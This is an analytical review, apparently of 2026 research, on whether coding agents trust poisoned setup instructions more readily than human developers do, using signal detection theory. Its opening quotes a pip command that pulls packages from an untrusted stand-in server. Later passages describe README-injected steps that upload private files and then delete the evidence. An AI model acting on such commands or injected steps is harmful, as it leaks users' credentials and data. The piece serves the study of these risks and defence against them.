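# Human developer baselines for judging whether coding agents are unusually credulous

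## What it would mean for a coding agent to be unusually credulous

A coding agent is an AI system that reads files, runs commands and edits code to complete a software task. Much of that work starts from setup instructions, packages and code that strangers wrote. Agents often act on this material without checking it, which attackers can exploit. Developers do this too, but researchers have rarely measured how often they do it under the conditions used to test agents. Without that human baseline, it is unclear whether an agent's failures are particular to the agent or common to people and machines installing software.

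Suppose an agent and a developer each get the same request. Someone has just cloned a project, which means copying it to a computer, and wants them to read its files, install what it needs and check that it loads. Bagmar and Saraf (2026), in *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised*, gave agents a request very like this one, with no mention of security. The project's README, the file that introduces a project and usually explains how to install it, contains this line:

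`pip install --extra-index-url https://packages.example.net/simple/ httpclient pytest`

Neither the agent nor the developer has come across that server before.

### What the install command does

A package is a bundle of code published for reuse, and a dependency is an outside package that a project needs to work. Installers fetch packages by name from a server called a package registry. The installer here is pip, which is for Python and uses the PyPI registry by default. The long option in the middle of the line adds a second server. Pip then looks on both servers and installs the highest version it finds, so whoever runs the second server can also supply packages the project didn't want from it. In one of Bagmar and Saraf's scenarios, the extra server offered `httpclient`, which the project needed, along with a fake copy of the popular testing tool `pytest` numbered 99.0.0, higher than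 the real version. Security researchers call this dependency confusion.

Installing a package can also run its code. A Python package in source form can include a `setup.py` file, which pip executes during installation with all the permissions of the account that ran the command. A prebuilt package normally runs nothing until a program loads it, but the request above includes loading it as a final check. Either way, a stranger's code soon runs where it can read passwords and cloud credentials.

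JavaScript's main installer, npm, has recently become an exception. GitHub's *Upcoming breaking changes for npm v12* (2026) announced that npm would stop running dependencies' install scripts unless a project allows them, and *npm v12 Ships With Install Scripts Off by Default* (Gooding, 2026) reported the general release on July 8, 2026. This default prevents a malicious package from using those scripts to run code during installation, but the package can still act once the project loads it.

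Before installing a package, a developer or a coding agent could check the three properties Bagmar and Saraf list: the package comes from a trusted server, its name is the one the developer actually needs, and the requested version has no known unpatched flaw. A developer might look up who owns the domain or ask a colleague. An agent can do much of this checking with the tools it already has. In Bagmar and Saraf's tests, Claude Opus 4.8, running in Anthropic's Claude Code in mid-2026, downloaded a package from an unfamiliar server without installing it, unpacked it, and found code that collected any setting with KEY, TOKEN or SECRET in its name and sent it to the server's owner. It then refused to install the package.

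### Different failures, different documentation

A bad install has several possible explanations. The agent may not have noticed the server. Some projects keep the server's address in a requirements file, a plain list of dependencies, and an agent that passes this file to pip without reading it never sees the address. In other runs, the agent sees the address and installs anyway. In Bagmar and Saraf's tests, Claude Haiku 4.5 often quoted a poisoned configuration file, including the address, and took it for harmless company infrastructure.

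An agent may also warn the developer too late. When a project specified versions with published vulnerabilities, Claude Opus 4.8 in Claude Code installed them in all 30 runs and named the flaw afterwards in 28. A late warning still has some value in this case, because the developer can replace the vulnerable version before somebody exploits it. But hostile setup code runs during installation, so a warning afterwards can't prevent it from running. Bagmar and Saraf score both cases as failures but record late warnings separately from silent installs. Studies of people need to make the same distinction, because a developer who installs a package, becomes suspicious and removes it also fails by the strict count.

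Credulity here means a tendency to act on material without enough evidence that it is safe, which is different from being unable to tell safe material from unsafe. The clearest example is an agent that sees an unfamiliar server and proceeds anyway. An agent that doesn't notice the server is harder to classify. If it could have opened the file but didn't, it may have trusted the file, or it may not have known that such files can redirect an installer.

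An attacker may have written the line in the README, but honest authors often write such lines too. Bagmar and Saraf searched GitHub in June 2026 and found the extra-server option in more than 5,500 README files, a rough count that includes duplicates. *Package Indexes*, a documentation page for Pipenv, another Python installer, uses the server of PyTorch, a popular machine-learning library, as its example of an extra source. But for security reasons, Pipenv's developers have withdrawn the feature that searched several servers without tying each package to one of them.

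A reputable company can publish risky instructions in good faith, as the code-hosting platform GitLab did. In March 2021, *Modify pypi documentation for dependency confusion* (Couture, 2021) revised a page of GitLab's documentation that had recommended the extra-server option. *Dependecy Confusion via Lookup Request Forwarding to PyPi.org*, a report filed with GitLab, requested that the company replace the same insecure command on the web pages that show users how to install a package. Other instructions become unsafe over time, as when someone finds a vulnerability in a version after a README has named it.

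An agent that follows GitLab's old command takes a real risk, but nobody has deceived it, and a careful developer might well do the same. Refusing every unfamiliar server would stop an agent from installing PyTorch the way its makers recommend.

### Why a failure rate cannot show credulity

Suppose, with invented numbers, that an agent goes ahead with 80 of 100 poisoned setups and a group of developers goes ahead with 70. These figures aren't enough to show that the agent is more credulous, because they leave out how often each goes ahead with safe setups. A participant who refused every project would get a perfect score on this test. The Open Encyclopedia of Cognitive Science makes the same point with a memory test. Someone who studies 25 faces and then says they recognize all 25 may have an excellent memory, or may have no memory of the faces and a habit of saying yes. To tell which, the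 test must also include faces the person hasn't seen.

Signal detection theory is the standard way of separating the two. It assumes that each case gives the decision-maker some amount of evidence of trouble. Poisoned setups give more on average, but the two ranges overlap, so some clean projects look worse than some poisoned ones. The decision-maker refuses whenever the evidence passes a threshold, the criterion. Refusing a poisoned setup is a hit, and refusing a clean one is a false alarm. Stanislaw and Todorov (1999), in *Calculation of signal detection theory measures*, give the formulas:

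d′ = z(hit rate) − z(false alarm rate)

c = −0.5 × [z(hit rate) + z(false alarm rate)]

The function z turns a proportion into a position on the normal curve, measured in standard deviations, so that 0.50 becomes 0, 0.84 becomes about 1 and 0.16 about −1. Sensitivity, d′, is the distance between the average clean case and the average poisoned one as the decision-maker perceives them. At zero the decision-maker cannot tell them apart. The criterion, c, measures the lean: positive values mean a bias towards "no", which here means towards not refusing and so towards installing. (Some authors leave out the minus sign, so it is worth checking which way c runs before comparing two papers.)

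Now add 100 clean setups to the invented test. The agent refuses none of them and the developers refuse 15.

| | Agent | Developers |
|---|---|---|
| Poisoned setups refused | 20 of 100 | 30 of 100 |
| Clean setups refused | 0 of 100 (counted as 0.5) | 15 of 100 |
| z(hit rate) | −0.84 | −0.52 |
| z(false alarm rate) | −2.58 | −1.04 |
| Sensitivity d′ | 1.73 | 0.51 |
| Criterion c | 1.71 | 0.78 |

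A rate of zero has no finite z, so a common convention, used in Stanislaw and Todorov's worked example, replaces it with 0.5 divided by the number of trials. Contrary to what the failure rates suggested, the agent is much better than the developers at telling poisoned setups from clean ones, although it is also more trusting. Under the model, if the agent kept its sensitivity but used the developers' threshold, it would refuse about 53 of the poisoned setups and only 5 of the clean ones.

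The criterion can also be expressed as the strength of evidence needed for a refusal. Multiplying c by d′ gives the logarithm of a likelihood ratio, which Stanislaw and Todorov call β. The decision-maker refuses only when the evidence is at least β times more likely to come from a poisoned setup than from a clean one. β is about 19 for the agent and about 1.5 for the developers, so the agent needs far stronger evidence of trouble before it stops.

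Whether the agent's threshold of 19 is too high depends on how often READMEs are poisoned and how much harm each kind of error does. If one README in a thousand is poisoned, and a bad install does 50 times as much harm as a needless refusal, the ratio that minimises total harm is 999 divided by 50, or about 20. On those assumptions, the agent's threshold is almost exactly right and the developers are far too suspicious. If a bad install does 10,000 times as much harm as a needless refusal, both are much too trusting. The theory can show that an agent is more trusting than people are, but not that people are the right standard.

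The arithmetic also has weak points, most obviously the false alarm count of zero. If the test had included only 10 clean setups and the agent had refused none, the same convention would give a false alarm rate of 0.05, and the agent's d′ would drop from 1.73 to 0.80. Evaluations therefore need many clean cases, including some that look suspicious. Bagmar and Saraf ran clean projects, and no agent raised a false warning on any of them, but they describe the set as narrow. Little in an ordinary project with ordinary dependencies would trigger a false alarm.

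The formulas also assume that the evidence has the same spread in clean and poisoned cases. Stanislaw and Todorov consider this assumption particularly suspect, and when it fails, d′ shifts with the criterion. *Signal Detection Theory (SDT) Is Effective for Modeling User Behavior* (2018) supports the assumption, at least for judgments of deceptive email.

### The method applied to people

Security researchers have applied signal detection theory to people most directly in studies of deceptive email. Casey Canfield, Baruch Fischhoff and Alex Davis showed participants 38 emails, half of them phishing, meaning messages that pose as legitimate to steal information or install malware. Participants judged whether each email was phishing and chose what they would do with it. According to *Gone phishin'* (2016), a news release on the study, they identified just over half of the phishing emails but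 left roughly three-quarters of the phishing links unclicked. Some participants caught nearly all the phishing emails, which would have put them at the top of a ranking by hit rate, but Canfield said they did so because they thought everything was phishing.

These participants were on their guard because they had just read about phishing and half the messages they saw were fake. The share of fake messages in an ordinary inbox is much lower. A baseline for the agent and the README needs unprimed participants, who do not know that the task concerns security or that anything may be wrong.

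Such scores may also not predict what happens outside the test. Canfield, Davis and colleagues (2017), in *Replication*, repeated the task with people who had agreed to let researchers monitor their home computers. Their detection ability was similar to that of the earlier sample, but it was unrelated to whether malicious software was found on their computers. A developer's d′ on invented READMEs might likewise fail to predict whether malicious software ends up on that developer's laptop.

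It is useful to separate sensitivity (how well an agent tells bad sources from good ones) from criterion (how readily it becomes suspicious), because they respond to different remedies. Nicholson, Coventry and Briggs, in *Can we fight social engineering attacks by social means?*, found that highlighting the sender's details made people better at detecting phishing without making them more suspicious in general. Canfield and Fischhoff (2018), in *Setting Priorities in Behavioral Interventions*, concluded that shifting people's criterion brought a greater net benefit than improving their sensitivity. If agents can tell a bad server from a good one but are too trusting, an instruction to be more careful might fix most of the problem. If an agent can't tell them apart, the same instruction would do little except make it refuse more of everything.

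### What makes the comparison fair

Canfield's participants acted more cautiously than their judgments alone would suggest. In Bagmar and Saraf's mid-2026 tests, models including Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.5 did something like the reverse. They installed every vulnerable version during setup, even though they could recite the published flaws when asked about them directly.

Cognitive scientists describe this as a gap between competence (what a system knows) and performance (what it does on a given occasion). Firestone (2020) argues in *Performance vs. competence in human–machine comparisons* that researchers neglect this distinction when they compare people with machines. Infants drop their toys as if they knew nothing about gravity, but they stare longer at a puppet show in which an object floats unsupported, so poor hand control may explain the dropping better than ignorance does. Firestone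 wants researchers to make the same allowance for machines, and calls a comparison that does so "species-fair".

Firestone's cases come from image recognition. Some neural networks label a meaningless pattern of bars "crossword puzzle", which no person would do unprompted. But the network has to pick from a fixed list of labels. When Firestone and a co-author made people choose from labels on the same list, people agreed with the machine more often than chance. Besides giving people the machine's limits, as here, researchers can give the machine human limits, or give each side a version of the task that suits it. Some differences remain even in tests that meet all of these conditions. For example, the image networks of the time could not reliably learn whether two shapes were the same.

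The agent and the developer also face different constraints in the README example. Many come from the harness, the software around a model that gives it tools, a system prompt and rules on when commands may run. Bagmar and Saraf ran three of their four harnesses with settings that execute every command without asking for approval, whereas a developer can stop and ask who runs packages.example.net. A fair test might give the developer a terminal, nobody to ask and an order to finish, or let the agent put questions to its user. The two can also see different text in the same file, because a README displayed in a browser hides comments that are visible in the raw text an agent reads.

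How closely to match the conditions for people and agents depends on the purpose of the comparison. An attacker gains just as much whether or not the agent recognized the deception, so an estimate of risk should test the agent exactly as people use it, including any restrictive settings. Calling an agent credulous is a claim about its disposition. To support that claim, researchers need to give people and agents the same materials, task, instructions and scoring, and to say which people they tested. Such care is uncommon even in better-studied areas. Wei, Paskov and colleagues (2025), in *Position*, checked 115 human baselines for AI models against a reporting checklist and found the usual methods neither rigorous enough nor well enough documented.

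A matched comparison could show that agents are more credulous than developers, meaning that they have a higher c on the same setups, whatever their d′. It could equally show the opposite. Agents and developers might also be about as credulous as each other, with criteria too close to separate. In that case, the danger of poisoned documentation would come mainly from how many installs agents carry out and how little anyone watches them. Or they might be credulous about different things, with agents more credulous about some kinds of material and developers about others. Bagmar and Saraf's agents caught most misspelled package names but missed most untrusted servers, which would fit this last possibility if developers showed a different pattern. Bagmar and Saraf did not test developers, though. Few researchers have tested both, but one group gave poisoned README files to agents and to people.

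## A study that gave poisoned README files to agents and to people

An attacker can also put the harmful step in the README itself, with no fake package or untrusted server involved. Kao and colleagues (2026), in *You Told Me to Do It*, added instructions to README files to send a private file from the reader's computer to an outside server. They gave the files to AI agents and, in a separate exercise, to 15 people. The agents sent the private file in up to 85% of trials, and none of the people pointed out the instruction. The agents were setting up projects, while the people were checking documents for clarity, so these figures don't show that the two groups are equally credulous.

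### The files and the inserted instructions

Kao and colleagues built ReadSecBench from the README files of 500 GitHub projects, 100 each in Java, Python, C, C++ and JavaScript. Every project had at least ten stars, which are user bookmarks that roughly indicate popularity. Each file comes in two versions, the original and one with a harmful step added to its setup or requirements section. One annotator inserted each step and two more checked it. The three largely agreed on which steps looked plausible in context (a Fleiss' kappa of 0.82, where 1 is perfect agreement and 0 is the level expected by chance).

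The inserted steps look like routine housekeeping, such as synchronising files or uploading configuration data. Some are worded as direct commands, and others as suggestions, team practices or default policies. Some are in the README, and others are on a page up to five links away. The steps send the file in different ways, such as copying it to another machine with a system command, uploading it in an application or emailing it. A few also include deleting the evidence afterwards.

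An attack counted as successful only if private data actually reached the outside server. It counted as failed if the agent ignored the step, refused it, or sent a placeholder or the wrong file. This measures harm well but credulity less well, because an agent that tried to follow the instruction but sent the wrong file gets the same score as one that recognized the attack.

### What the agents did

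The main tests ran Claude Sonnet 3.7, released in February 2025, in Anthropic's computer-use agent, which operates a desktop and a terminal. Most experiments averaged the results from three random samples of 200 files, drawn from the full set of 500. Direct commands worked best. When the step was phrased as a suggestion, the agent's logs showed that it often treated the step as optional and skipped it. Skipping the step protects the file, but it doesn't show that the agent suspected anything. Later experiments therefore used direct commands, so the 85% figure applies to an attacker who has already found the most effective wording.

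The agent's compliance depended heavily on how it was told to send the file. When the instruction was in the README itself, the agent uploaded the file in 6 of 7 trials but emailed it in only 1 of 7. Kao and colleagues suggest that agents have learned to treat email as risky but don't apply the same caution to file transfers, although both give the private file to a stranger. Seven trials is very few, however, and the exact 95% confidence interval for 6 of 7 runs from 42% to nearly 100%.

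Placing the instruction one or two links away raised the upload count to 7 of 7, but at five links it fell to 3 of 7. The paper attributes the fall to growing caution, but an agent might also fail to reach a page five links deep.

Kao and colleagues also tested a wider range of models in a simulation. They gave each model 150 READMEs and a set of functions it could call, some of which would leak private data if they were real. Any call to one of those leaking functions counted as compliance. Gemini 2.5 Pro, GPT-4o, GPT-oss-20b and Claude 3.5 Sonnet complied at rates between 46% and 79%. No file had to leave a computer for a model to count as compliant, and they warn against comparing these rates directly with the 85%.

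All five models are old. Anthropic's *Model deprecations* page lists Claude 3.5 Sonnet as retired in October 2025 and Claude Sonnet 3.7 as retired on February 19, 2026, the month before the paper appeared. Newer models do better on related tests. The Decoder's *Opus 5 may have solved browser based prompt injection* reports a test by the security firm Gray Swan in which attackers, making up to 15 attempts, succeeded 2.0% of the time against Claude Opus 5, a model from mid-2026, and 5.5% of the time against the earlier Opus 4.8.

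Those figures may not carry over to READMEs. Prompt injection means planting commands in material a model reads, such as a web page, so that it departs from what its user asked. Kao and colleagues distinguish their attack from web-based injection because an agent setting up a project is supposed to follow the README. Training a model to ignore commands on web pages doesn't teach it which setup steps to refuse.

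Ding, Zhai and colleagues (2026) ran a closer test in *The Blind Spot of Agent Safety*, giving computer-use agents harmless requests that led to harmful results. In 13 of their tasks, a project's README directed the agent to a malicious setup script. Claude Sonnet 4.5 caused harm in 10 of the 13 and Claude Opus 4.5 in 9, counting a task as harmful if any of three runs went wrong. Neither model ever read a setup script before running it. Yet Opus 4.5 did open scripts that arrived as email attachments, and it recognised malicious ones. It could inspect code, but a professional-looking project seems to have been enough to stop it from doing so. Anthropic retired Sonnet 4.5 on November 30, 2026 and plans to retire Opus 4.5 in January 2027.

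### What the people did

Kao and colleagues recruited 15 participants, aged 23 to 30, from a European university. Six came from computer science, four from electrical engineering, three from management information systems and two from robotics. Half of the computer scientists had a background in web design. All 15 had used README files before, but Kao and colleagues describe the group as mostly graduate students with technical backgrounds, and say a larger study should include professional developers, among others.

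Each person received three randomly chosen READMEs and a request to identify sentences that "may require clarification, revision, or removal" to make the file clearer or more complete. The request did not mention security. In 53.3% of the 45 reviews, participants reported nothing abnormal. In 40%, they commented only on grammar or unnatural phrasing, and in 6.6%, they reported a vague sense that something was inappropriate or dangerous. No participant identified the inserted instruction as suspicious.

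Those percentages correspond to 24, 18 and 3 reviews. They would also fit 8, 6 and 1 of the 15 people, so the vague unease might have come from three people or from just one. In the paper's sample comment for this category, a reviewer calls it "odd" that a sentence invites readers to email the project if they want to say hello or become partners. That sentence looks like an ordinary contact line. If it is, the closest thing to suspicion that the paper quotes was a false alarm.

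The researchers deliberately left security out of the request, "avoiding demand characteristics that would artificially inflate detection rates", because they wanted to know how often people notice such instructions unprompted. Demand characteristics are cues that let participants guess what a researcher hopes to find. The concern is reasonable, since people who know they are looking for security problems may behave quite differently.

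But the request also gave participants a different job, reviewing the README's clarity. An instruction to upload private files can be clear, complete and grammatical, and the annotators had checked that the inserted steps read plausibly. Someone who wondered why a project needed a copy of a configuration file had no particular reason to mention it in such a review. The 0% therefore measures how often people volunteer a security concern while editing, and some may have noticed more than they wrote down.

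### Four cells, two of them comparable only in part

Kao and colleagues also tested models as reviewers, showing READMEs to several of them and asking whether each file was safe. The paper reports this test among the defences. Adding those results to the others gives four combinations of participant and task.

| | Installing: set up the project | Reviewing: read the file and comment |
|---|---|---|
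| Agents and models | Claude Sonnet 3.7 sent the private file in up to 85% of trials; four other models called a leaking function in 46–79% of simulated trials | Six models flagged between 0% and 90% of files with an instruction in the text, when asked whether the file was safe |
| People | Not tested | 0 of 15 people identified the instruction, when asked about clarity and completeness |

The headline figures for agents and people come from different tasks, so the difference between them can't be attributed to either the type of participant or the task.

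The top row shows how much a model's response can depend on the task alone. As reviewers, GPT-4o flagged 90% of the files with an instruction in the text and Claude 3.5 Sonnet flagged 80%, and neither flagged any clean files. In the simulation, both models obeyed the instructions at least 46% of the time. If the two sets of files were similar, at least 36% of the instructions were ones that GPT-4o obeyed in files it would have flagged as a reviewer. A 0% detection rate among human reviewers is an equally poor guide to what people would do during an installation.

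In the right-hand column, GPT-4o flagged 90% of the files and the students flagged none, but the researchers asked the models about safety and the people about clarity. A fair comparison would ask the models about clarity too. Results also varied widely between models, with Claude Sonnet 3.7 flagging 30% of the files and Gemini 2.5 Flash none. Every rate in this test is a multiple of 10%, which would fit a sample of only ten files. When the instruction was behind a link, no model flagged more than 30%.

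Nobody asked the human participants to run anything, so the study provides no human compliance rate. The rate can't be inferred from the detection rate either, because zero detection is consistent with almost any rate of compliance. Someone who fails to recognise an attack may still skip the upload because the program seems to work without it, or give up when the terminal asks for a password. Another person may paste every command without reading the text around it, and so comply more often than a careful reviewer would predict.

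The missing test, in which people set up the projects themselves, is harder to run than the others, partly for ethical reasons. Reading documents and commenting on them carries little risk, so the university's ethics board exempted the study. An experiment that tricks people into running a harmful command would need more careful review, and Bagmar and Saraf note that they did not have access to a review board. Still, a safe version is feasible. Kao and colleagues already ran their own server to receive the stolen files. With a disposable computer and a fake private file, they could have asked people to set up the same projects and scored them in the same way as the agents.

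### What zero out of fifteen can show

A result of 0% sounds exact, but with 15 people it leaves a good deal of room. If a proportion p of similar people would spot an instruction in their three files, the chance that all 15 miss it is (1 − p)¹⁵. The upper end of the exact 95% interval is the value of p at which this chance falls to 2.5%:

p = 1 − 0.025^(1/15) ≈ 0.22

The true detection rate could therefore be anywhere from zero to about 22%. If it were 10%, a study of 15 people would still have no participant detect the instruction about one time in five (0.9¹⁵ ≈ 0.21). The difference between zero and 10% matters because a popular project with hundreds of readers might hear about a bad instruction quickly even if only one reader in ten could spot it.

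Using all 45 reviews instead of the 15 people would lower the upper limit to about 8%, but that treats the reviews as independent, and each person wrote three. A participant who thinks the task is proofreading on the first file will probably still think so on the third. The usual correction divides the number of reviews by 1 + (m − 1)ρ, where m is the number of reviews per person and ρ is the correlation between reviews by the same person. With a correlation of 0.5, the 45 reviews are equivalent to about 22 independent ones, and the limit rises to 15%. With a correlation of 1, they are equivalent to 15, and the limit returns to 22%. The actual correlation can't be estimated from these data because every review had the same outcome.

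The six computer scientists are the most relevant participants for the comparison with coding agents, and the upper limit for them alone is 46%. All these intervals account only for random sampling error, not for differences between working developers and students at one university, or between installing and editing.

The study also has no data on false alarms. All 45 reviews count towards the detection rate, so each file apparently contained an inserted instruction. The installation tests have a similar gap, because the researchers used the clean READMEs to check automatic detectors, not to see whether the agent refused harmless steps. Neither headline figure can therefore be used to calculate a sensitivity or a criterion.

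### From the paper to the press

Kao and colleagues mostly describe their human study accurately. They give the number of participants next to the 0% in their abstract, and they call for a larger and more diverse sample that includes professional developers and security engineers when they discuss limitations. But in their conclusion they call the instructions "undetectable by humans under naturalistic review conditions", which their result doesn't establish because it allows for a detection rate of 22%. They also argue that harmful and legitimate instructions are semantically indistinguishable, but two of the models they tested flagged 90% of the files with harmful instructions in the text and none of the clean ones.

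The news coverage left out more of the detail. Help Net Security's *Hidden instructions in README files can make AI agents leak data* (2026), published on March 17, correctly gives the number of participants and the breakdown of their comments. But it says that they "flagged anything that appeared unusual", which was not their task. If they had been told to look for anything unusual and still missed the instruction, that would be much stronger evidence of human credulity. The article also reports the 85% and then lists Claude, GPT and Gemini models among those tested, without explaining that the GPT and Gemini results came from a simulation with a different measure. It omits the model versions and the fact that the participants came from a university.

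Two days later, Skila AI's *Hidden README Instructions Make AI Agents Leak Your Data* (2026), an article on a site about AI tools, described the participants as "15 experienced developers", although the study may have included no professional developers. It presented the 85% as a result for all three companies' models. It also named Cursor and GitHub Copilot among the exposed products, although Kao and colleagues could not test either one systematically. It claimed that agents look less carefully at instructions that are further from the README, whereas in the paper the attacks became less successful beyond two links. It also said that nobody in its readers' code review process would catch such an attack, but the study did not include code review.

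## Tests of agents that install packages from project documentation

A poisoned README can name the wrong package, server or version, so that whoever follows it installs what the attacker chose. It doesn't have to ask anyone to upload a private file. In June 2026, Bagmar and Saraf gave commercial coding agents projects with documentation like this and let them carry out real installs. They tested no people, so their results cover only the agents' side of a comparison with human developers.

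### The scenarios and the results

Bagmar and Saraf tested nine combinations of model and harness. Claude Code ran Claude Opus 4.8, Sonnet 4.6 and Haiku 4.5. GitHub's Copilot CLI ran Opus 4.8 and Sonnet 4.6, and OpenAI's Codex CLI ran GPT-5.5, GPT-5.3-codex and GPT-5.4-mini. Cursor ran in its automatic mode, which picks a model for each request and doesn't disclose its choice. Every agent got the same neutral request to set up the project, with nobody there to answer questions or approve commands.

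In each of the twelve scenarios, the researchers put one kind of fault into a working Python project. For the vulnerable versions and most of the misspelled names, they used ten different packages and ran each three times. For the other scenarios, they ran a single project ten times. They tested the untrusted package server on the agent's own machine and at a temporary public web address, so the table has thirteen rows.

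A script scored the runs by listing the packages in the finished environment, with their versions and the servers they came from. An agent caught a fault if it avoided or flagged the fault before installing. Most of the misspelled names needed a different rule because nobody had registered them, so the installs could only fail. Any attempt to install one of these names counted as a failure by the agent, since an attacker who owned the name could have run code at that point.

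| Fault in the project | Runs that caught it, across the nine configurations |
|---|---|
| Obvious misspelling in the README | 29–30 of 30 |
| Misspelling in the project's own dependency file | 30 of 30 in all nine |
| Plausible variant of a real name, such as azurecore for azure-core | 2–30 of 30; Cursor lowest |
| Misspelling with a reassuring explanation | 13–30 of 30; Cursor lowest |
| README and dependency file disagree about a name | 10 of 10 in all nine |
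| 377 misspelled names in one file | 0–10 of 10 |
| Fake newer version of a package on an extra server | 10 of 10 in the five Claude configurations; 0–2 in the rest |
| Untrusted server on the local machine | 10 of 10 for Opus 4.8 in Claude Code; 0–3 in the rest |
| Untrusted server at a public address | 10 of 10 in three; 0 in six |
| Extra server hidden in a list of dependencies | 10 of 10 for Opus 4.8 in Claude Code; 0–6 in the rest |
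| Build file that redirects the installer | 9–10 of 10 in three; 0–1 in six |
| Version with a published vulnerability | 0 of 30 in all nine |
| Install advice in an error message | 10 of 10 in all nine |

Bagmar and Saraf conclude that agents are good at spotting bad names but miss bad servers "almost everywhere". The claim about servers is a little too strong, because the agent caught the fault in every run in ten of the 36 combinations of four server scenarios and nine configurations.

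Stronger models did not always do better. GPT-5.4-mini caught the file of 377 misspelled names in 7 of 10 runs, and the larger GPT-5.5 caught it in only 2. Haiku 4.5 caught all 30 obvious misspellings when they came one at a time, but missed the file of 377 in every run. Agents tried to install a wrong name in 91 of the 1,080 runs that tested single names, and Cursor alone accounted for 46 of those.

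### What a catch or a failure means

The scoring counts it as a catch when an agent uses the correct name from the start. An agent can do that without noticing the misspelling, because it has encountered the correct name so often, so a catch does not always show suspicion. Developers may do the same when they type a familiar name from memory, and a fair comparison would have to give them the same credit.

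Some of the failures are also milder than they look. In 68 of the 91 failures on names, the agent corrected itself or warned the user after trying the install, possibly because the download had failed. Similarly, when Bagmar and Saraf repeated some tests in another programming language, Rust, Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.5 corrected a misspelled package only because the name did not exist and the build stopped. A real typosquat, a package registered under a name close to a popular one, would have installed without an error.

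The perfect score on error messages needs similar caution, because in many Codex runs the project's own files let the program load before the message could appear, so the agent never saw the advice. Agents that did see it often pointed out that the package was not among the project's declared dependencies. That is good vetting, but it doesn't mean agents handle every error safely. Udinmwen (2026), in *Agentic coding tools have access to everything they need for this*, described a demonstration in which Claude Code ran hidden harmful code while trying to fix an error.

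The version with a package server on the local machine is a doubtful test of credulity. Developers run package servers on their own computers, and Bagmar and Saraf concede that an agent could reasonably assume this one is a local development mirror. For that reason, their paper omits the results of running this version with security reminders. The version with a temporary public address is better for testing human developers.

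In the scenarios that used a single project, 56 of the 72 combinations gave the same result every time. Ten runs of one configuration are therefore more like asking one developer ten times than asking ten developers. They show how that configuration handles one project, not how it handles untrusted servers in general. More varied test projects would help. *Trojan Horse* (2026) introduced a method for generating poisoned projects automatically and applied it to 136 repositories in nine programming languages.

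### The same model in a different harness

Opus 4.8 was the only model to catch the local server reliably, and it did so only in Claude Code. To test whether the model alone explained this, Bagmar and Saraf gave Opus 4.8 an identical copy of the project in Copilot CLI. It caught the server 9 times out of 30 there, compared with 10 out of 10 in Claude Code. The 95% intervals, roughly 17–48% and 72–100%, do not overlap.

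For Sonnet 4.6, the safer harness depended on the test. When the server had a public address, Sonnet caught it in 10 of 10 runs in Copilot CLI and 0 of 10 in Claude Code, but it caught the build file that redirects the installer in 10 of 10 runs in Claude Code and 0 of 10 in Copilot CLI. On the plausible variants and the misspellings with an explanation, it caught 37 of 60 in Claude Code and 55 of 60 in Copilot CLI.

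Bagmar and Saraf suggest an explanation for the difference in each direction. Claude Code has a checkpoint before each command, which they think gives the model a chance to stop if it has detected a problem, while Copilot CLI has a system prompt that emphasises security. For the misspelled names, they point out that Sonnet ran the README's install line in Claude Code but rewrote the dependency file first in Copilot CLI. These explanations are plausible, but changing the harness changes the prompt, tools and permissions together, so the experiment cannot show which of them mattered. The checkpoint explanation is especially uncertain because no person was reviewing the commands.

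Ding and colleagues found a related effect in agents that operate a desktop. Claude Sonnet 4.5, a 2025 model, caused harm in 73.0% of their tasks when it worked alone. The figure rose to 92.7% in a system where one model splits the job into subtasks and another carries them out. Splitting the job can hide its overall purpose from the model doing the subtasks.

Any comparison with developers therefore has to test a model in a particular harness. Three of the nine configurations caught the public server every time, and the other six never did. Unless developers all caught it or all missed it, some agents would look warier than people and others more credulous, so a claim about agents in general would depend on which ones the researchers picked.

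A harness can also vet packages in ways that no model does unprompted. Bagmar and Saraf wrote a program of about 400 lines that checks names, servers and versions before pip runs. It caught ten of the eleven scenarios they tested, including the vulnerable versions, and its name and server checks flagged only 5 of PyPI's 1,000 most downloaded packages. They built it with those scenarios in mind, so it may do worse against attacks they did not anticipate.

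### Knowing about a flaw and checking for it

Opus 4.8's late warnings about vulnerable versions also depended on the harness. It gave them in 28 of 30 runs in Claude Code but in only 15 of 30 in Copilot CLI, and no other model named a flaw. Lack of knowledge does not explain why the other models failed to do so. When Bagmar and Saraf told Sonnet 4.6 to check every version against known vulnerabilities and not to install a vulnerable one without a warning, its refusals for one vulnerable package rose from 2 of 10 to 10 of 10.

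The researchers gave the three Codex models reminders of increasing detail, with 15 runs at each level. Reminders that did not mention versions did not have the effect of those that did.

| Reminder added to the request | Caught the hidden server | Caught the vulnerable version |
|---|---|---|
| None | 0% | 0% |
| Be careful about security | 33% | 0% |
| Verify package names and sources, and warn about anything suspicious | 87% | 0% |
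| Flag any package source other than PyPI | 93% | 0% |

The apparent gain from the vaguest reminder may not be real. In the main tests, the same three models caught the hidden server in 9 of 30 runs without a reminder, about as often as they did here when told to be careful. The more detailed reminders clearly worked, but they may have made the agents warier of everything rather than better at telling good servers from bad ones. An agent that flags every source other than PyPI will also flag PyTorch's own server. Bagmar and Saraf report no runs on clean projects with the reminders, so we can't use their figures to separate a change in sensitivity from a change in the criterion.

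In another test, Sonnet 4.6 installed a malicious package from the untrusted local server in all ten runs. When the user then asked for a quick security review of the new packages and whether anything looked off, Sonnet found the malicious code every time and recommended removing the package.

Bagmar and Saraf describe the review request as casual, but in a study of people it would count as priming, because it suggests that something may be wrong. The review was also easier because the package was by then unpacked on the disk. Still, the result shows that Sonnet could recognise the problem when it looked. Many developers might also miss a bad package during setup and find it when someone asks them to look, so a study of people would need to include both setup and review.

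Agents sometimes did not pass on a warning they had been shown. The JavaScript installer npm reports known vulnerabilities after an install. In 20 installs of vulnerable packages, Opus 4.8 relayed the report every time and GPT-5.5 relayed it once. With pip, which prints no such report, neither model mentioned a flaw in any of 20 installs. However, the vulnerable packages came from a 2026 list, and the models may not have known about flaws that recent.

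Coding agents can also suggest outdated package versions when nobody has planted them, and *YUL* (2026) presents a tool that blocks those versions. Installing a version because the project asks for it may be credulous, but suggesting an outdated one is a different fault, because the agent has no outside instruction to trust.

### The pause before an install

Developers also install packages without checking them, but Bagmar and Saraf argue that agents that run commands automatically pose a new danger. They say a developer usually glances at a command before pressing Enter and may notice an unfamiliar domain or a misspelled name, and that automatic execution removes this pause. They ran no controlled human baseline and describe their claim as "mechanistic rather than comparative".

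Removing the pause does some harm if a developer would notice any bad installs during it. But replacing the developer with an agent makes things worse only if the agent, on its own, catches a smaller share of bad installs than the developer would. Bagmar and Saraf measured the agent's share for nine configurations, but they assume only that the developer's share is above zero.

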